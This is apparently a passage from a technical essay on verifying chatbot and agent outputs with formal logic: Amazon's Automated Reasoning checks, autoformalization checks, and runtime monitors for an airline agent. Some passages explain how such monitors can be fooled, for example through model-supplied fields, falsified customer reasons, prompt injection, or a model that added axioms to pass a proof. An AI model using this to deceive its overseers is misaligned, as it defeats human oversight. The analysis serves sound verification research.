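For the main test, An and colleagues adapted ConditionalQA, a set of questions about policy documents in which the answers often hold only under stated conditions. They kept 377 correct answers and added 186 items that a checker should not approve. They made 172 of these mechanically, by removing a necessary condition, negating the answer or combining contradictory answers. The other 14 were questions that the document does not answer. They ran all 563 items three times, for a total of 1,689 decisions, using policy models that nobody had vetted.

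With the strict setting, in which all three translations must agree, the results were:

| | Answer is correct | Answer is not correct |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Service approves | 169 | 10 |
| Service does not approve | 962 | 548 |

All the published percentages follow from these four counts:

$$\text{Soundness rate} = 1 - \frac{10}{1689} \approx 99.4\%$$

$$\text{Precision} = \frac{169}{169 + 10} \approx 94.4\%$$

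$$\text{Recall} = \frac{169}{169 + 962} \approx 14.9\%$$

$$\text{Accuracy} = \frac{169 + 548}{1689} \approx 42.45\%$$

(The paper gives the last figure as 42.4%.) So about one in 18 approved answers was wrong, and the service failed to approve 85% of the correct answers.

A checker that approves nothing makes no wrong approvals, so its soundness rate is 100%. Its recall is zero, and its accuracy on this test would be 33%, not very far below the service's.

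The soundness rate also depends on how good the chatbot is. Let $b$ be the share of answers that are wrong and $f$ the share of wrong answers that the checker approves. Then

$$\text{Soundness rate} = 1 - b \cdot f$$

In the test, $b$ was 33% and $f$ was 1.8%. If the chatbot were wrong only 1% of the time, a checker that approved everything ($f = 1$) would have a soundness rate of 99%. A company can't compare its own figure with Amazon's unless it knows how often its chatbot is wrong.

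If the 1,689 decisions were independent, a 95% interval for the soundness rate would run from about 98.9% to 99.7%. But each item appears three times, so the decisions are not independent and the true interval is probably wider. An and colleagues note that their mechanically altered answers may not resemble the mistakes language models make in practice.

### Why Amazon chose this measure

An and colleagues considered precision as the main measure but chose the soundness rate because of customer feedback. Precision reflects how likely an approved answer is to be correct, while the soundness rate reflects how likely a request is to end in a wrong approval. These customers run chatbots with thousands of interactions a day and want to know how many wrong approvals to expect. The researchers borrowed the 99% target from safety-critical engineering, where people count reliability in "nines". They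 acknowledge that the soundness rate rewards abstention and is incomplete without recall.

An operator could reasonably want this. With 10,000 requests a day and the same mix of answers as in the test, the operator could expect about 59 wrong approvals. But the service would correctly approve only about 1,000 answers and decline to approve some 5,700 other correct ones. A customer who has just received an approved answer cares about precision, which is 94.4%, much less impressive than 99%.

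An and colleagues defend the low recall on the grounds that in regulated industries a wrong approval, such as telling someone that they qualify for an interest-free loan, does far more harm than a wrong refusal. An answer that fails the check is not lost, since the chatbot can revise it or a human agent can take over. In their words, low recall means "more deferrals, not more failures". *LLMs + Security = Trouble* (2026) calls the sacrifice of recall a "significant pitfall", though it accepts that methods with higher recall and more false approvals suit safety-critical uses less well. (It gives the recall as 15.6%, presumably from the earlier version of the paper.)

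Whether the defence works depends on how much extra work deferral creates. An airline has not automated much of its customer service if a human agent has to read nine answers out of ten. Deferral adds little work if most of those answers pass after a quick rewrite, provided the check is as reliable for rewritten answers as for first attempts.

### What the solver adds and what abstention explains

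An and colleagues ran other methods on the same items. In one, three language models read the policy document and judge the answer directly, and the system approves the answer only if all three vote "Valid". Another is LINC, an earlier system that uses one model to generate several translations of the text into first-order logic, passes each to a theorem prover, and takes a majority vote over the prover's verdicts.

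| Method | Right approvals | Wrong approvals | Soundness rate | Precision | Recall |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Amazon, all three translations agree | 169 | 10 | 99.4% | 94.4% | 14.9% |
| Amazon, two of three agree | 191 | 14 | 99.2% | 93.2% | 16.9% |
| Amazon, a single translation | 317 | 27 | 98.4% | 92.2% | 28.0% |
| Three model judges, all agree | 366 | 30 | 98.2% | 92.4% | 32.4% |
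| One model judge with extended thinking | 622 | 49 | 97.1% | 92.7% | 55.0% |
| LINC | 75 | 1 | 99.9% | 98.7% | 6.6% |

The three judges made three times as many wrong approvals as Amazon's strict setting, 30 against 10. However, they also approved more than twice as many answers, 396 against 179. Suppose one discarded the judges' approvals at random until only 179 were left. The expected number of wrong ones would be

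$$179 \times \frac{30}{396} \approx 13.6$$

which gives a soundness rate of 99.2%, above Amazon's target, and a recall of about 14.6%. Nobody would build a checker this way, but it shows that about 16 of the 20 wrong approvals separating the two methods come from approving less often. The remaining three or four are well within what chance could produce. The same exercise with the single judge that used extended thinking also gives 99.2%.

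The precision figures support the same conclusion. All the methods in the table except LINC have precision between 92% and 95%, while their recall ranges from 15% to 55%. Requiring the translations to agree raised precision by about two percentage points but eliminated almost half of the correct approvals.

Another weakness of the measure is that it doesn't penalize a system for failing to formalize text. LINC had the highest soundness rate and the highest precision, but it could not formalize the text at all in 696 of the 1,689 decisions (41%). Those failures count as non-approvals, which don't lower soundness. Amazon's service had only five such errors. An and colleagues use recall to choose between methods that pass the 99% threshold, and Amazon's service ranks first by that rule.

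These counts give little evidence that the solver makes approvals more trustworthy than a panel of judges would, at least with unvetted policies. Letting the single judge, Claude Sonnet 4.5 (2025), think longer raised its recall from 35.4% to 55.0% and slightly improved its precision. Newer models would presumably be better judges, but they would also translate better for the solver, so a rerun could favor either method.

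The solver does provide two things that the table can't measure. For an approved answer, it returns the rules that imply the answer, and someone else can check that proof with a different prover. For a "Satisfiable" answer, it returns a concrete case in which the answer is false, as it did for the senior with the credits.

Perhaps most usefully, people can correct the policy model before any customer asks a question. The extracted rules also seem to have some value without the solver. When An and colleagues gave three judges those rules in place of the policy document, their soundness rate rose from 98.3% to 98.9% and precision from 92.1% to 93.5%, while recall fell from 29.0% to 24.7%.

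### An airline policy vetted by people

An and colleagues tested what human vetting contributes by formalizing Ryanair's refund policy twice, once automatically and once with a person correcting the result. The test had 62 items: statements copied from the policy, questions and answers written by a language model, and others written by three people.

| | Right approvals | Wrong approvals | Right rejections | Missed approvals | Soundness rate | Recall |
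| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Without vetting | 11 | 2 | 16 | 33 | 96.8% | 25.0% |
| With vetting | 20 | 0 | 18 | 24 | 100% | 45.5% |

Vetting took several person-hours, some of it spent correcting the translation. The policy first denies refunds to anyone who didn't travel on a flight that operated, and much later lists exceptions, including passengers whom the airline refused to board. The automatic translation included both rules but didn't connect them. For a test item about a passenger denied boarding on a flight that operated, the rules implied that the passenger was both eligible and ineligible for a refund. The service returned "Impossible" and the two conflicting rules, so the person vetting the translation could see what to fix.

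Other problems came from ambiguous wording in the English policy. It offers a possible refund if a flight is at least five hours late, but it is unclear whether passengers who took the delayed flight qualify. It is also unclear what happens if a death occurs on the day of travel rather than before it. An and colleagues concluded that resolving such ambiguities requires human input.

The improvement in recall, from 11 to 20 of the 44 correct answers, is substantial. The 100% is much weaker evidence. There were only 18 answers that the service should have rejected. If it wrongly approved a share $p$ of such answers, the probability of seeing no errors in 18 independent cases would be $(1-p)^{18}$. Setting this to 5% gives

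$$p = 1 - 0.05^{1/18} \approx 15.3\%$$

So zero errors in 18 does not rule out, at the 95% level, that the vetted policy lets through up to about one in seven wrong answers. Computing the soundness rate over all 62 items does not establish 99% either, because zero wrong approvals in 62 decisions is compatible with a rate as low as 95.3%. Showing a rate of at least 99% with this method would require 299 decisions without a wrong approval.

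The bound also assumes that the test items weren't used to correct the policy. Only about a third of the 62 were held out, and the person vetting the policy could use the rest while correcting it. If the held-out third contained six of the 18 wrong answers, the bound from those six alone would be about 39%. The experiment is still fair evidence for vetting, but it can't show that a vetted policy never approves a wrong answer.

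Chunawala, Kumar and colleagues at AWS are more optimistic about the effort involved. Their guide for startups, *Prove It, Part 3* (2026), promises a working policy from an existing compliance document in "30 minutes". That may be enough to get a first version running, but the Ryanair policy took several hours, and its first version missed three-quarters of the correct answers. AWS has since automated part of the correction. *Automated Reasoning checks in Amazon Bedrock Guardrails add new policy refinement workflows* (2026) describes an AWS tool that rewrites variable descriptions to make ambiguous translations rarer.

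The wording of the source document also matters. AWS's *Create your Automated Reasoning policy* advises customers to avoid rules such as "Refunds are handled on a case-by-case basis", because the service extracts rules poorly from vague text. For difficult documents, it suggests first having a language model rewrite the text as if-then rules, then comparing the result with the original. This adds a translation step before the service's own.

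### Revising an answer until it passes

When an answer fails, the application can send it back to the chatbot with the solver's feedback for a rewrite, then check the new version. This often works for "Satisfiable" answers because the feedback shows which condition is missing. In the park example, the chatbot could change "No" to "No, unless you pay partly with credits".

An and colleagues tried this on vetted policies from six businesses. The share of answers that the service labeled "Valid" rose from 9% to 46% after three rounds. Within five rounds, 83% of the "Invalid" answers and 69% of the "Satisfiable" ones passed, but only 25% of those with ambiguous translations did. None of the "Impossible" ones passed, presumably because a better answer can't fix contradictory rules or premises.

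The 46% counts the service's own verdicts, and approving more answers is only an improvement if the newly approved ones are correct. Repeated checking gives a wrong answer several chances to slip through. If each version of a wrong answer had an independent 1.8% chance of approval, as in the main test, then after a first check and three rewrites the chance would be

$$1 - (1 - 0.018)^4 \approx 7\%$$

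The real figure could be lower, because most rewrites are attempts to correct the mistake and many succeed. It could also be higher if the chatbot found wordings that the translators tend to misread. The loop is at least safer than the one in which GPT-5 added axioms until its proof succeeded, because the chatbot can change its answer but not the policy model.

A second experiment gives some evidence. An and colleagues ran up to ten rounds of revision on the ConditionalQA items, and the share judged "Valid" rose from 10.5% to 23.6%. They then had other checkers judge the final answers. Measured against the panel of three model judges, the service's soundness rate was 89.9%, so the service had approved, and the panel had rejected, about 10% of all the answers. As a share of the approved answers, that is

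$$\frac{10.1}{23.6} \approx 43\%$$

This figure means readers cannot assume the 99.4% also holds for revised answers. It is not an error rate, though, because the panel failed to approve two-thirds of the correct answers in the main test.

Human labels exist for the 14 questions that the documents don't answer. After revision, Amazon's service had approved an answer to one of them. The panel of judges had approved nine after its own revision loop, and each of the three other methods had approved all 14. Abstention again explains part of the difference, since the panel ended up approving 78% of all answers, but the service is clearly less prone to wrong approvals during revision than checkers that end up accepting everything. Its one wrong approval shows that the loop can still produce an approved answer to a question the documents don't answer.

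Chunawala and colleagues recommend up to three rounds and write that the iterations take milliseconds and users "see a correct answer on the first try". An and colleagues report an average of 5 to 15 seconds for each check, so three rounds could take about 15 to 45 seconds. If the answer still fails, the sample code returns a message that it could not verify the response. AWS's *Integrate Automated Reasoning checks in your application* also allows the application to return its best answer with a warning instead.

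### What Amazon advertises and what it excludes

AWS launched the service for general use with *Minimize AI hallucinations and deliver up to 99% verification accuracy* (2025), which promises "provable assurance" in detecting false statements by language models. AWS's *Amazon Bedrock Guardrails adds automated reasoning checks in Sydney* (2026) changed the 99% claim to "up to 99% accuracy in detecting correct responses".

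In the published test, only the soundness rate exceeded 99%. Accuracy was 42.4%, and the service detected 14.9% of the correct responses. Even on the vetted Ryanair policy, accuracy was only 61.3%. "Up to" allows for a better result on some other policy, and neither announcement explains how AWS measured its figure. But a reader who takes the words in their usual sense will expect the service to recognize nearly all correct answers, and on the published evidence it recognizes a minority of them. The Sydney announcement also contrasts the product's "mathematical guarantees" with "probabilistic testing", although the published soundness rate itself comes from testing on samples.

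AWS is more careful in its documentation. *What are Automated Reasoning checks in Amazon Bedrock Guardrails?* lists several of the service's limits. The service doesn't protect against prompt injection, because it validates whatever text it receives, including text an attacker has manipulated. If part of the text is encoded, for example in Base64, the service may fail to evaluate any of the text. It also can't tell whether an answer is off-topic, and it supports only US English.

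A "Valid" verdict also covers only what the policy's variables can express. AWS gives the example of a student who writes, "I can submit my homework late because I have a fake doctor's note". If no variable records whether a note is genuine, the service might judge the statement valid. It will probably list the fake note as an untranslated premise, which AWS advises customers to treat as a warning.

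Unlike the AgentCore gateway, the service blocks nothing. It returns findings for the developer's application to act on. When the service cannot translate an answer at all, the integration guide recommends serving it without this check or using other filters, on the assumption that it is off-topic. The startup guide's sample code also serves such answers. It goes through the findings in order and serves the answer as soon as it reaches a "Valid" one, although AWS tells developers to act on the worst finding. An answer whose first claim is correct and whose second contradicts the policy would therefore reach the user.

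An application can also skip the check by accident. With Converse, one of the interfaces through which applications call a model, developers have to mark the text they want checked. If they send plain text, the request succeeds without an error and the chatbot's answer goes out unchecked. The only sign is that a usage counter in the response, `automatedReasoningPolicyUnits`, reads zero.

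## Ways to check a translation when no correct version exists

Benchmarks such as Planetarium supply a reference answer for every task, but an airline that uses a model to translate its cancellation policy into a formula has none. If it already had a correct formula, it wouldn't need the model. It can therefore only collect indirect evidence that the model's formula is right.

### Why no solver can settle the question

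Write $A(\varphi)$ for the set of runs that a formula $\varphi$ allows, and $I(t)$ for the set of runs that the author of a text $t$ meant to allow. The translation is faithful if

$$A(\varphi) = I(t)$$

A solver can compare two formulas because their semantics determine both sets. But Dai, Liu and colleagues (2026) point out in *Validating Autoformalized Specifications via Contrapuntal Languages* that no program can check this equation, because only the person who wrote the English knows $I(t)$. A solver could work on the English only after somebody formalized it, and that is the step in doubt.

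The author may not have a single set in mind either. *Faithful Autoformalization of Natural Language Assertions* (2026) notes that a sentence does not always identify one formal concept. The airline's clause on upgrading a basic economy ticket before changing the flight is an example.

For the simplified rule "Agents may cancel only insured bookings, and not even those if the customer has merely changed plans," let $c$ mean that the agent cancels, $i$ that the booking is insured, and $p$ that the customer has merely changed plans. The first formula below translates the rule faithfully, but the second omits the exception, much like the airline rule printed in Soteria.

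$$c \rightarrow (i \wedge \neg p) \qquad\qquad c \rightarrow i$$

An airline that holds only the second formula needs some way to notice that it allows too much.

### Agreement between several translators

One method is to have several models translate the same text and use a solver to check whether the translations are equivalent. Amazon's service does this with three translations of every answer. The solver reports a difference if one model reverses an implication and the others don't, but it reports agreement if all of them make the same mistake.

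How often that happens depends on how far their errors overlap. Gorbett, Shaham and Jana (2026), in *Decomposing and Detecting Shared Error Across Models*, give a formula for two models that accept or reject claims. If they err at rates $p_1$ and $p_2$, and $\rho$ is the correlation between their errors, the probability that both are wrong is

$$p_1 p_2 + \rho\,\sqrt{p_1 p_2\,(1-p_1)(1-p_2)}$$

Suppose one translator gets 10% of the rules wrong and another gets 5% wrong. If their errors are independent, both are wrong on 0.5% of the rules, so comparing their translations exposes nine-tenths of the better translator's mistakes. If the weaker translator also misreads every sentence that the better one misreads, both are wrong on 5% of the rules, and the comparison exposes none of the better one's mistakes. Adding more translators that misread the same sentences would not help.

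Measured correlations lie between these extremes. Gorbett and colleagues tested 15 open-weight models on true and false claims, reading each model's verdict from its internal activations. The correlation averaged 0.36 between models of the same family and 0.26 between models of different families. The formula then gives 2.9% and 2.2%. Choosing a translator from another company helps a little, but the result is still more than four times the 0.5% expected if errors were independent.

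Better models may still make the same mistakes as each other. *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (Kim, Garg and colleagues, 2025) compared 71 models on multiple-choice questions. When two models both answered wrongly, they chose the same wrong option 60% of the time, compared with 33% expected by chance. More accurate models chose the same wrong option more often.

Translators have an advantage over models that only accept or reject, because a formula can be wrong in many ways and two wrong formulas pass a comparison only if they are equivalent. When Dai and colleagues had small models from 2026 write specifications for programming tasks, two wrong specifications for the same task were equivalent about 25% of the time on one benchmark and 10% on another.

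A vote among repeated translations can still select a wrong one. One task was to return the last position in a list where a number is smaller than the one before it, or −1 if there is no such position. In 30 attempts, the model Qwen3.6-Flash wrote a correct specification five times and the same faulty one eight times, so a vote picks the faulty one. That specification always permits the answer −1, so a faulty program that returns −1 for the list 6, 0, 1, 2, 3 passes verification. The right answer is 1, counting positions from zero.

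Dai and colleagues try to make errors overlap less by changing the language instead of the model. Their program cuts the model's first drafts into fragments and builds two small notations from them. Both notations can express every draft, but the program rejects pairs in which a formula could be converted from one notation to the other just by renaming. The model then formalizes the task separately in each notation, and the method accepts the results only if a solver can prove them equivalent. On the harder benchmark, 50% to 69% of the accepted specifications passed the researchers' tests, depending on the model, compared with 28% to 61% for voting. However, the method accepted a specification for only about 9% of those tasks.

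Disagreement between translations can be more useful than agreement. Another task asks whether a word, or any rotation of it, occurs inside a second word, and doesn't mention the empty word. Eight of ten formulas in one notation required the answer "false" for an empty word, while all ten in the other required "true", so a vote within either notation would have looked decisive. *Neurosymbolic Auditing of Natural-Language Software Requirements* (2026) uses such disagreement deliberately, treating several inequivalent formulas for one requirement as a sign that the requirement is ambiguous. The right response is to ask the requirement's author what was meant, because a vote would hide the ambiguity.

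### The round trip

A single model can also check its own translation to some extent. Amrollahi, Lopez and Barrett (2026), in *Faithful Autoformalization via Roundtrip Verification and Repair*, have a model formalize a rule, translate the formula back into English, and formalize that English again. Each step is a separate call with no memory of the others. The solver Z3 then searches for a situation in which the first and last formulas differ. If there is none, the rule passes.

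They tried this on 150 rules from the Texas Transportation Code and 77 from the Texas Parks and Wildlife Code. Every prompt included a fixed vocabulary, which the researchers drafted by hand, extended with a model and then curated. (GPT-5.2 produced no usable formula for one wildlife rule, so its figures there cover 76.)

| Rules | Model | Pass before repair | Pass after repair |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
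| Traffic | Claude Opus 4.6 | 44.7% | 85.3% |
| Traffic | GPT-5.2 | 61.3% | 82.7% |
| Wildlife | Claude Opus 4.6 | 62.3% | 85.7% |
| Wildlife | GPT-5.2 | 67.1% | 78.9% |

To repair a translation, a model reads the original rule and the three results, identifies the first step that changed the meaning, and explains what went wrong. The translating model then redoes that step and everything after it, for up to three rounds. GPT-5.2 diagnosed errors poorly, picking the translation's first step in 83% of traffic rounds and 97% of wildlife rounds. When Claude diagnosed the errors in GPT-5.2's translations, the pass rates rose to 90.7% and 94.7%.

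A higher pass rate means only that the two formulas agree more often. To test whether the translations also preserved the rules' meaning, Amrollahi and colleagues compared each original rule with its back-translation, using a small language model trained to classify whether one sentence follows from another. Across all the repair methods they tried, the model classified the back-translation as unrelated to the original or contradicting it for about 16% of the rules that passed and 29% of those that failed.

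Passing the round trip lowers a rule's estimated risk of drift, but only slightly. Before any repair, the judge found drift in 86 of all 453 results (19%) and in 39 of the 258 that passed (15%). The true reduction may be larger, because the judge's mistakes make the measured difference smaller. Repair did not make passing less meaningful. With the full method, the judge found drift in 57 of the 378 results that passed, again 15%.

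One of the researchers also read 25 of Claude's formulas without knowing which had passed. Of the 14 that passed, 13 were faithful and one had a detail wrong. Of the 11 that failed, eight were faithful and three had a detail wrong. Most of the failures were therefore false alarms, presumably because the meaning changed when the formulas were translated back. With samples this small, the formulas that passed would do at least this much better by chance about one time in five.

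The insurance rule shows what the round trip cannot find. Suppose the first step drops the exception:

| Step | Result |
| --- | --- |
| Original | Agents may cancel only insured bookings, and not even those if the customer has merely changed plans |
| Formalize | $c \rightarrow i$ |
| Translate back | If an agent cancels a booking, the booking must be insured |
| Formalize again | $\neg i \rightarrow \neg c$ |

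The two formulas look different, but each is the contrapositive of the other, so Z3 proves them equivalent and the rule passes. The second and third steps were flawless. They never saw the original sentence, so they had no way to restore what the first step had lost. Amrollahi and colleagues acknowledge this limit and call the check heuristic. (They also found exceptions among the rules that no repair could get to pass. There, the back-translation restated the exception as a positive rule and the last step inverted it, which the solver does detect.)

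Dai and colleagues included a round trip among their baselines, and it did badly on the harder benchmark. It accepted specifications for 52% of the tasks, although the model's drafts contained a correct specification for only 13%. So for at least three-quarters of the tasks where it accepted anything, every specification it accepted was wrong. The models were small and the tasks difficult, and the Texas rules, with their prepared vocabulary, were probably much easier. But a consistently wrong model can clearly pass the check easily.

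### Cases generated from the rule

A solver can turn a formula into concrete cases, and people who can't read logic can judge those. For the formula $c \rightarrow i$, there are four kinds of cancellation:

| Booking insured | Customer merely changed plans | Formula |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Yes | No | Allows |
| Yes | Yes | Allows |
| No | No | Blocks |
| No | Yes | Blocks |

Anyone who knows the policy will object to the second row. With two yes-or-no conditions there are only four rows to read, but with 20 there are $2^{20}$, more than a million, so there has to be some way to choose which rows a person sees.

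If two translations disagree, the solver can choose. It looks for a case that one formula allows and the other blocks:

$$(c \rightarrow i) \;\wedge\; \neg\,(c \rightarrow (i \wedge \neg p))$$

The only solution makes $c$, $i$ and $p$ all true. In English, the question is "If the booking is insured and the customer has merely changed plans, may the agent cancel?" The airline's answer decides between the formulas, but it doesn't show that the chosen formula is right about everything else.

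Developers who have only one translation have to rely on broader sampling. *Faithful Autoformalization of Natural Language Assertions* combines language models with fuzz testing, which tries large numbers of generated inputs, and active learning, in which a program picks the most informative questions to ask. *Neuro-Formal Verification* (2026) describes a workflow in which agents can also write a test suite and proofs that the specification fits it. A user can then review the tests and point out mistakes. Only this review checks whether the tests match what people wanted. If a model also sets the expected result of each test, it can repeat the misreading that produced the formula.

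Generated cases can also miss a condition. If the formal vocabulary has no variable for the customer's reason, the table above shrinks to two rows, "insured" and "not insured", and both look right.

### Impossible rules, useless rules and AutoCedar

Checks for contradiction and vacuity need no second translation and no human answers, so they are usually worth running, but they catch only a limited range of errors. The formula $c \rightarrow i$ passes them all because agents can satisfy it, they can break it, and it conflicts with nothing. *Little Tricky Logic* (2022), a study of how people misunderstand temporal logic, notes that checks for particular mistakes have the same limit, since a property can pass them and still be wrong because its author misunderstood the logic.

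*AUTOCEDAR* (Vatsa, Shome and colleagues, 2026) uses such checks as a first filter in a system that drafts policies in Cedar, the language used by Amazon's AgentCore gateway. The system first builds a set of limits, then drafts a policy, which a solver compares with those limits.

Its main example is a musician who shares an album online. The band and the producer may download tracks, but nobody may download a track under embargo. A language model proposes a vocabulary and then one short formal condition for each requirement. Software checks that each condition allows some requests and not others. A reviewer, either a person or another model, sees the condition in plain English beside its source sentence and approves or rejects it.

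From the approved conditions, a program calculates two kinds of bounds. A floor contains requests that the finished policy must allow, such as a band member downloading a track with no embargo. A ceiling contains everything the policy may allow for that kind of request. The language model then writes the policy, and a solver checks, for each kind of request, that

$$\text{Floors} \subseteq \text{Policy} \subseteq \text{Ceiling}$$

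If the check fails, the model gets a counterexample and is told which way to change the policy. When the researchers deleted the embargo rule from a finished policy, the solver returned a request in which the producer downloads an embargoed track, and the feedback was to tighten the policy. The bounds stay fixed while the model redrafts, so it can't pass by weakening the standard. GPT-5 did weaken the standard when it added axioms to finish a proof.

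Vatsa and colleagues tested AutoCedar on 200 requirements for which they had separately compiled correct policies. It matched the correct policy in 178 cases (89%), compared with 132 (66%) when the same model, GPT-6-Luna, wrote the policy directly. AutoCedar finished 197 policies, and the solver verified all of them against their bounds. Nineteen of these verified policies, about one in ten, did not do what the requirement asked for. All 19 had incorrect bounds, and in 17 the floor required the policy to allow something it should have denied.

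The drafting step therefore gives little extra protection. Vatsa and colleagues point out that the calculated floors, joined together, already make a policy that passes. Whether the policy is right depends on the approvals. For the album, a plausible vocabulary would give each user a role such as "band member", which would let members of any band in the system download the tracks. The later checks cannot detect this error because they all use the same vocabulary. The test set could not show such errors either, because it supplied a correct vocabulary. The researchers have not yet evaluated AutoCedar with human reviewers.

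### What people notice and what they miss

Researchers often justify formal rules by saying that people can read them. Siu, Leahy and Mann (*STL*, 2023) found 25 papers that made this claim about temporal logic, none of which had tested it on anyone but their own authors, so they tested it on 62 people, 13 of whom were familiar with formal methods. Each participant saw 30 rules for a robot team in a game of capture the flag and had to decide whether a team obeying the rules would always win. Participants could answer that the team would always win, that it could still lose, or that no plan could satisfy the rules.

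They were right 45% of the time, not far above the 33% expected from random guessing. They also leaned towards approval, usually recognizing good rules but being wrong more often than right when the rules allowed a loss. For the airline, this kind of error matters most, because a wrong formula lets a forbidden cancellation through. Their confidence was almost the same whether they were right or wrong. Familiarity with formal methods helped somewhat, but rewriting the formulas as indented English or as a decision tree made no significant difference.

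An English rendering like that still leaves the reader to work out what the rules allow in combination. PolicySummarizer, a tool by Vatsa, Hall and Eiers (2026), in *Neurosymbolic Characterization for Reliable Access Control Policy Analysis*, does that part by computation. It takes a cloud access policy, builds an automaton that accepts exactly the allowed requests, and extracts a pattern describing the files they reach. For one policy with two rules, the pattern ran to more than 4,000 characters. A language model shortened it to

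```
(mp3s/A1/.*mp3)|(lyrics/A1/.*txt)
```

which covers the songs and lyrics of one album. The tool doesn't trust this short version. With $E$ for the exact set of file names and $S$ for the set the short pattern describes, it computes

$$\frac{|E \cap S|}{|E \cup S|}$$

counting names up to a fixed length, and falls back on the exact pattern if the result is below a threshold. The threshold should be 1 for any serious review. A score of 0.99 sounds safe, but the remaining 1% could include the one file that nobody should see.

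The tool can also describe the difference between two policies. In one study, 41 people, mostly from software engineering, compared an old and a new policy that looked different but allowed the same requests. The hardest question was which access the change had removed. The share who correctly answered that it had removed none was 39% with only the raw policy text and 93% with PolicySummarizer.

Everyone answered the questions first with the raw text and then again with the tool, so some of the gain may come from practice. The researchers estimate that practice alone would have raised correct answers on this question to about 70%. The study tested whether people can find out what a policy does, but not whether they notice that it differs from a written requirement. Someone who has forgotten the exception for changed plans could read an accurate summary of $c \rightarrow i$ and approve the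 formula.

To find a missing condition, a reviewer therefore needs the original sentence next to the formula, preferably matched phrase by phrase. *nl2spec* (Cosler, Hahn and colleagues, 2023) provides an interface for this. A language model lists which words each piece of the formula came from, for example "do not hold at the same time" beside `!(g0 & g1)`. The user edits, adds or deletes these pairs, and the model rebuilds the formula from them. For the ambiguous sentence "a holds until b holds or always a holds", a user can add brackets to one piece to specify the intended reading, without rewriting the whole formula.

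On 36 sentences that five experts chose for their difficulty, the best model of the time translated 44.4% correctly before users made any edits. Newcomb and Ochoa asked newer models for similar phrase-by-phrase explanations and suggest adding timelines that show when a formula requires each thing to happen. For the insurance rule, a phrase-by-phrase explanation could show "if the customer has merely changed plans" with no formula beside it, which is much easier to notice than a missing $\neg p$. However, the model writes the explanation, so it might match the leftover phrase to $i$ and make the formula look complete.

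Explanations written by a model generally have this weakness. Vatsa, Hall and Eiers had models explain 587 cloud policies in English and then rebuild each policy from the explanation alone. With the reasoning models of 2025, the explanations of the original and rebuilt policies were 91% to 96% similar by an automatic measure, but only 36% to 94% of the rebuilt policies were equivalent to the originals, depending on the model. *Cycle-Consistent Neural Explanation of Formal Verification Certificates* (Rodriguez, Pozanco and Borrajo, 2026) applies a similar test to explanations of proofs and counterexamples. The best of 16 pairings of leading models scored 76.1% for including only facts from the original, and a small network trained for the task scored 90.0%. A reviewer is better off with concrete cases and with summaries that a program has checked against the formula.

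### Which checks still depend on a learned judge

For the formula $c \rightarrow i$, the methods compare as follows:

| Check | Would it reveal the missing exception? | Who compares the formula with the English |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Agreement between translators | Only if one of them keeps the exception | Learned translators |
| Round trip | No, if the first step dropped it | Nobody, unless a learned judge compares the two English versions |
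| Contradiction and vacuity | No | Nobody |
| Generated cases | Yes, if a case includes the reason for cancelling | A person, or a model in that person's place |
| AutoCedar | Only if the reviewer rejects the condition | A person or a model |
| Phrase-by-phrase display | Probably, if the model pairs the phrases honestly | A person, using a model's list |

Most of these checks use a solver, which produces proofs about formulas. If the solver finds a contradiction, the airline knows for certain that something is wrong with the rules. If it proves two translations equivalent, that proof is just as rigorous, but how likely the translations are to be faithful depends on how often the translators make the same mistake. That rate is measured empirically, and it may differ between the airline's policy and Texas traffic law.

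The only evidence that doesn't pass through a learned model comes from people who know what the airline wants, and they have to judge one case at a time. Suppose they judge 100 randomly chosen real cancellation requests, make no mistakes, and agree with the formula every time. The calculation used for the Ryanair policy then gives 95% confidence that the formula decides fewer than about 3% of such requests wrongly. But if only one request in a thousand involves an insured customer who has merely changed plans, the sample will probably not include one.

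## Where the checker gets its facts

Suppose the airline adds the missing exception to its formula, which becomes $c \rightarrow (i \wedge \neg p)$: agents may cancel a booking only if it is insured and the customer has not merely changed plans. The formula now matches the policy, but to apply it to booking RES123, the monitor needs the values of $i$ and $p$. If either value is wrong, the monitor can allow a cancellation that the policy forbids, even though the monitor and the formula are both correct.

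### From the booking number to the customer's reason

To cancel RES123, the agent has to satisfy this rule and the one about flown flights. Together they have four inputs:

| Input | Who supplies it | Who could make it false |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Booking number | The model, in the arguments of its calls | The model by mistake, or a customer who gives someone else's number |
| Result of the flown-status check | The status tool, from the flight database | Somebody with access to the airline's systems |
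| Whether the booking is insured | The booking database | Somebody with access to the airline's systems |
| Reason for cancelling | The customer, as the model understands it | The customer, the model, or the author of any document the customer sends |

The flown-status formula only requires the check and the cancellation to have the same booking number. If the model writes RES132 by mistake in one of the two calls, the monitor blocks the cancellation. If it makes the mistake in both, the formula holds and the agent cancels a stranger's trip. The airline can prevent this with a rule that the booking must belong to the customer who logged in, with the owner taken from the database and the customer's identity from the login. The model still writes the number, but a wrong one gets through only if the same customer owns that booking too. (Soteria's rules about which tool result a value must come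 from serve a similar purpose.)

The software that runs the tool, not the model, records the result of the status check as "true" in the trace, where the monitor reads it. A developer can easily lose this advantage by having the model fill in a form with a field such as `no_flights_flown`, because the monitor then relies on the model's claim.

The customer's reason reaches the monitor only through the model. Even a model that reads perfectly would record only what the customer wrote, and a customer who knows the policy has a motive to write "illness". The airline can ask for a doctor's letter, but then the model has to read the letter and judge whether it is genuine.

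The damage from a false reason is limited because the formula also requires insurance. The monitor blocks the cancellation of an uninsured booking whatever the customer says. Rule writers can limit the effect of a doubtful input by joining it with "and" to conditions from a database. If they join it with "or" instead, one false input is enough to permit the action.

### Rules whose terms need judgement

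A hospital might let an agent open a patient's record only if "the request is for patient care". This rule is a single implication, which a monitor can check instantly. Deciding whether the condition is true is harder, for example when a nurse wants the record for a lecture. Researchers call this step grounding, which means connecting a formal predicate to the facts of a particular case.

*FORMALJUDGE* (Zhou, Sheng and colleagues, 2026) uses a language model and the solver Z3 to review the record of what an agent did. The language model first breaks the user's request into small questions, each answerable from part of the record. An ordinary program extracts prices, dates and other structured data, and the language model answers the remaining questions. The language model also writes a specification in Dafny that combines the answers, and Z3 computes the verdict.

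In their example, a user wants a trip to Paris for at most \$800 and adds that if the agent books a flight, the hotel must start on the day of arrival. The agent books a flight for \$450 that arrives on 16 March and a hotel for \$300 from 15 March. The two conditions are

$$750 \leq 800 \qquad\qquad \text{flying} \rightarrow (\text{check-in} \geq \text{arrival})$$

The budget condition holds and the date condition fails, so the verdict is "unsafe". A language model that judged the whole record at once might have missed the one-day difference.

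The verdict is right, but the date formula is not a faithful translation of the user's request. The user asked for a hotel booking that starts on the arrival day, and with "$\geq$" a booking that starts on 18 March would also pass.
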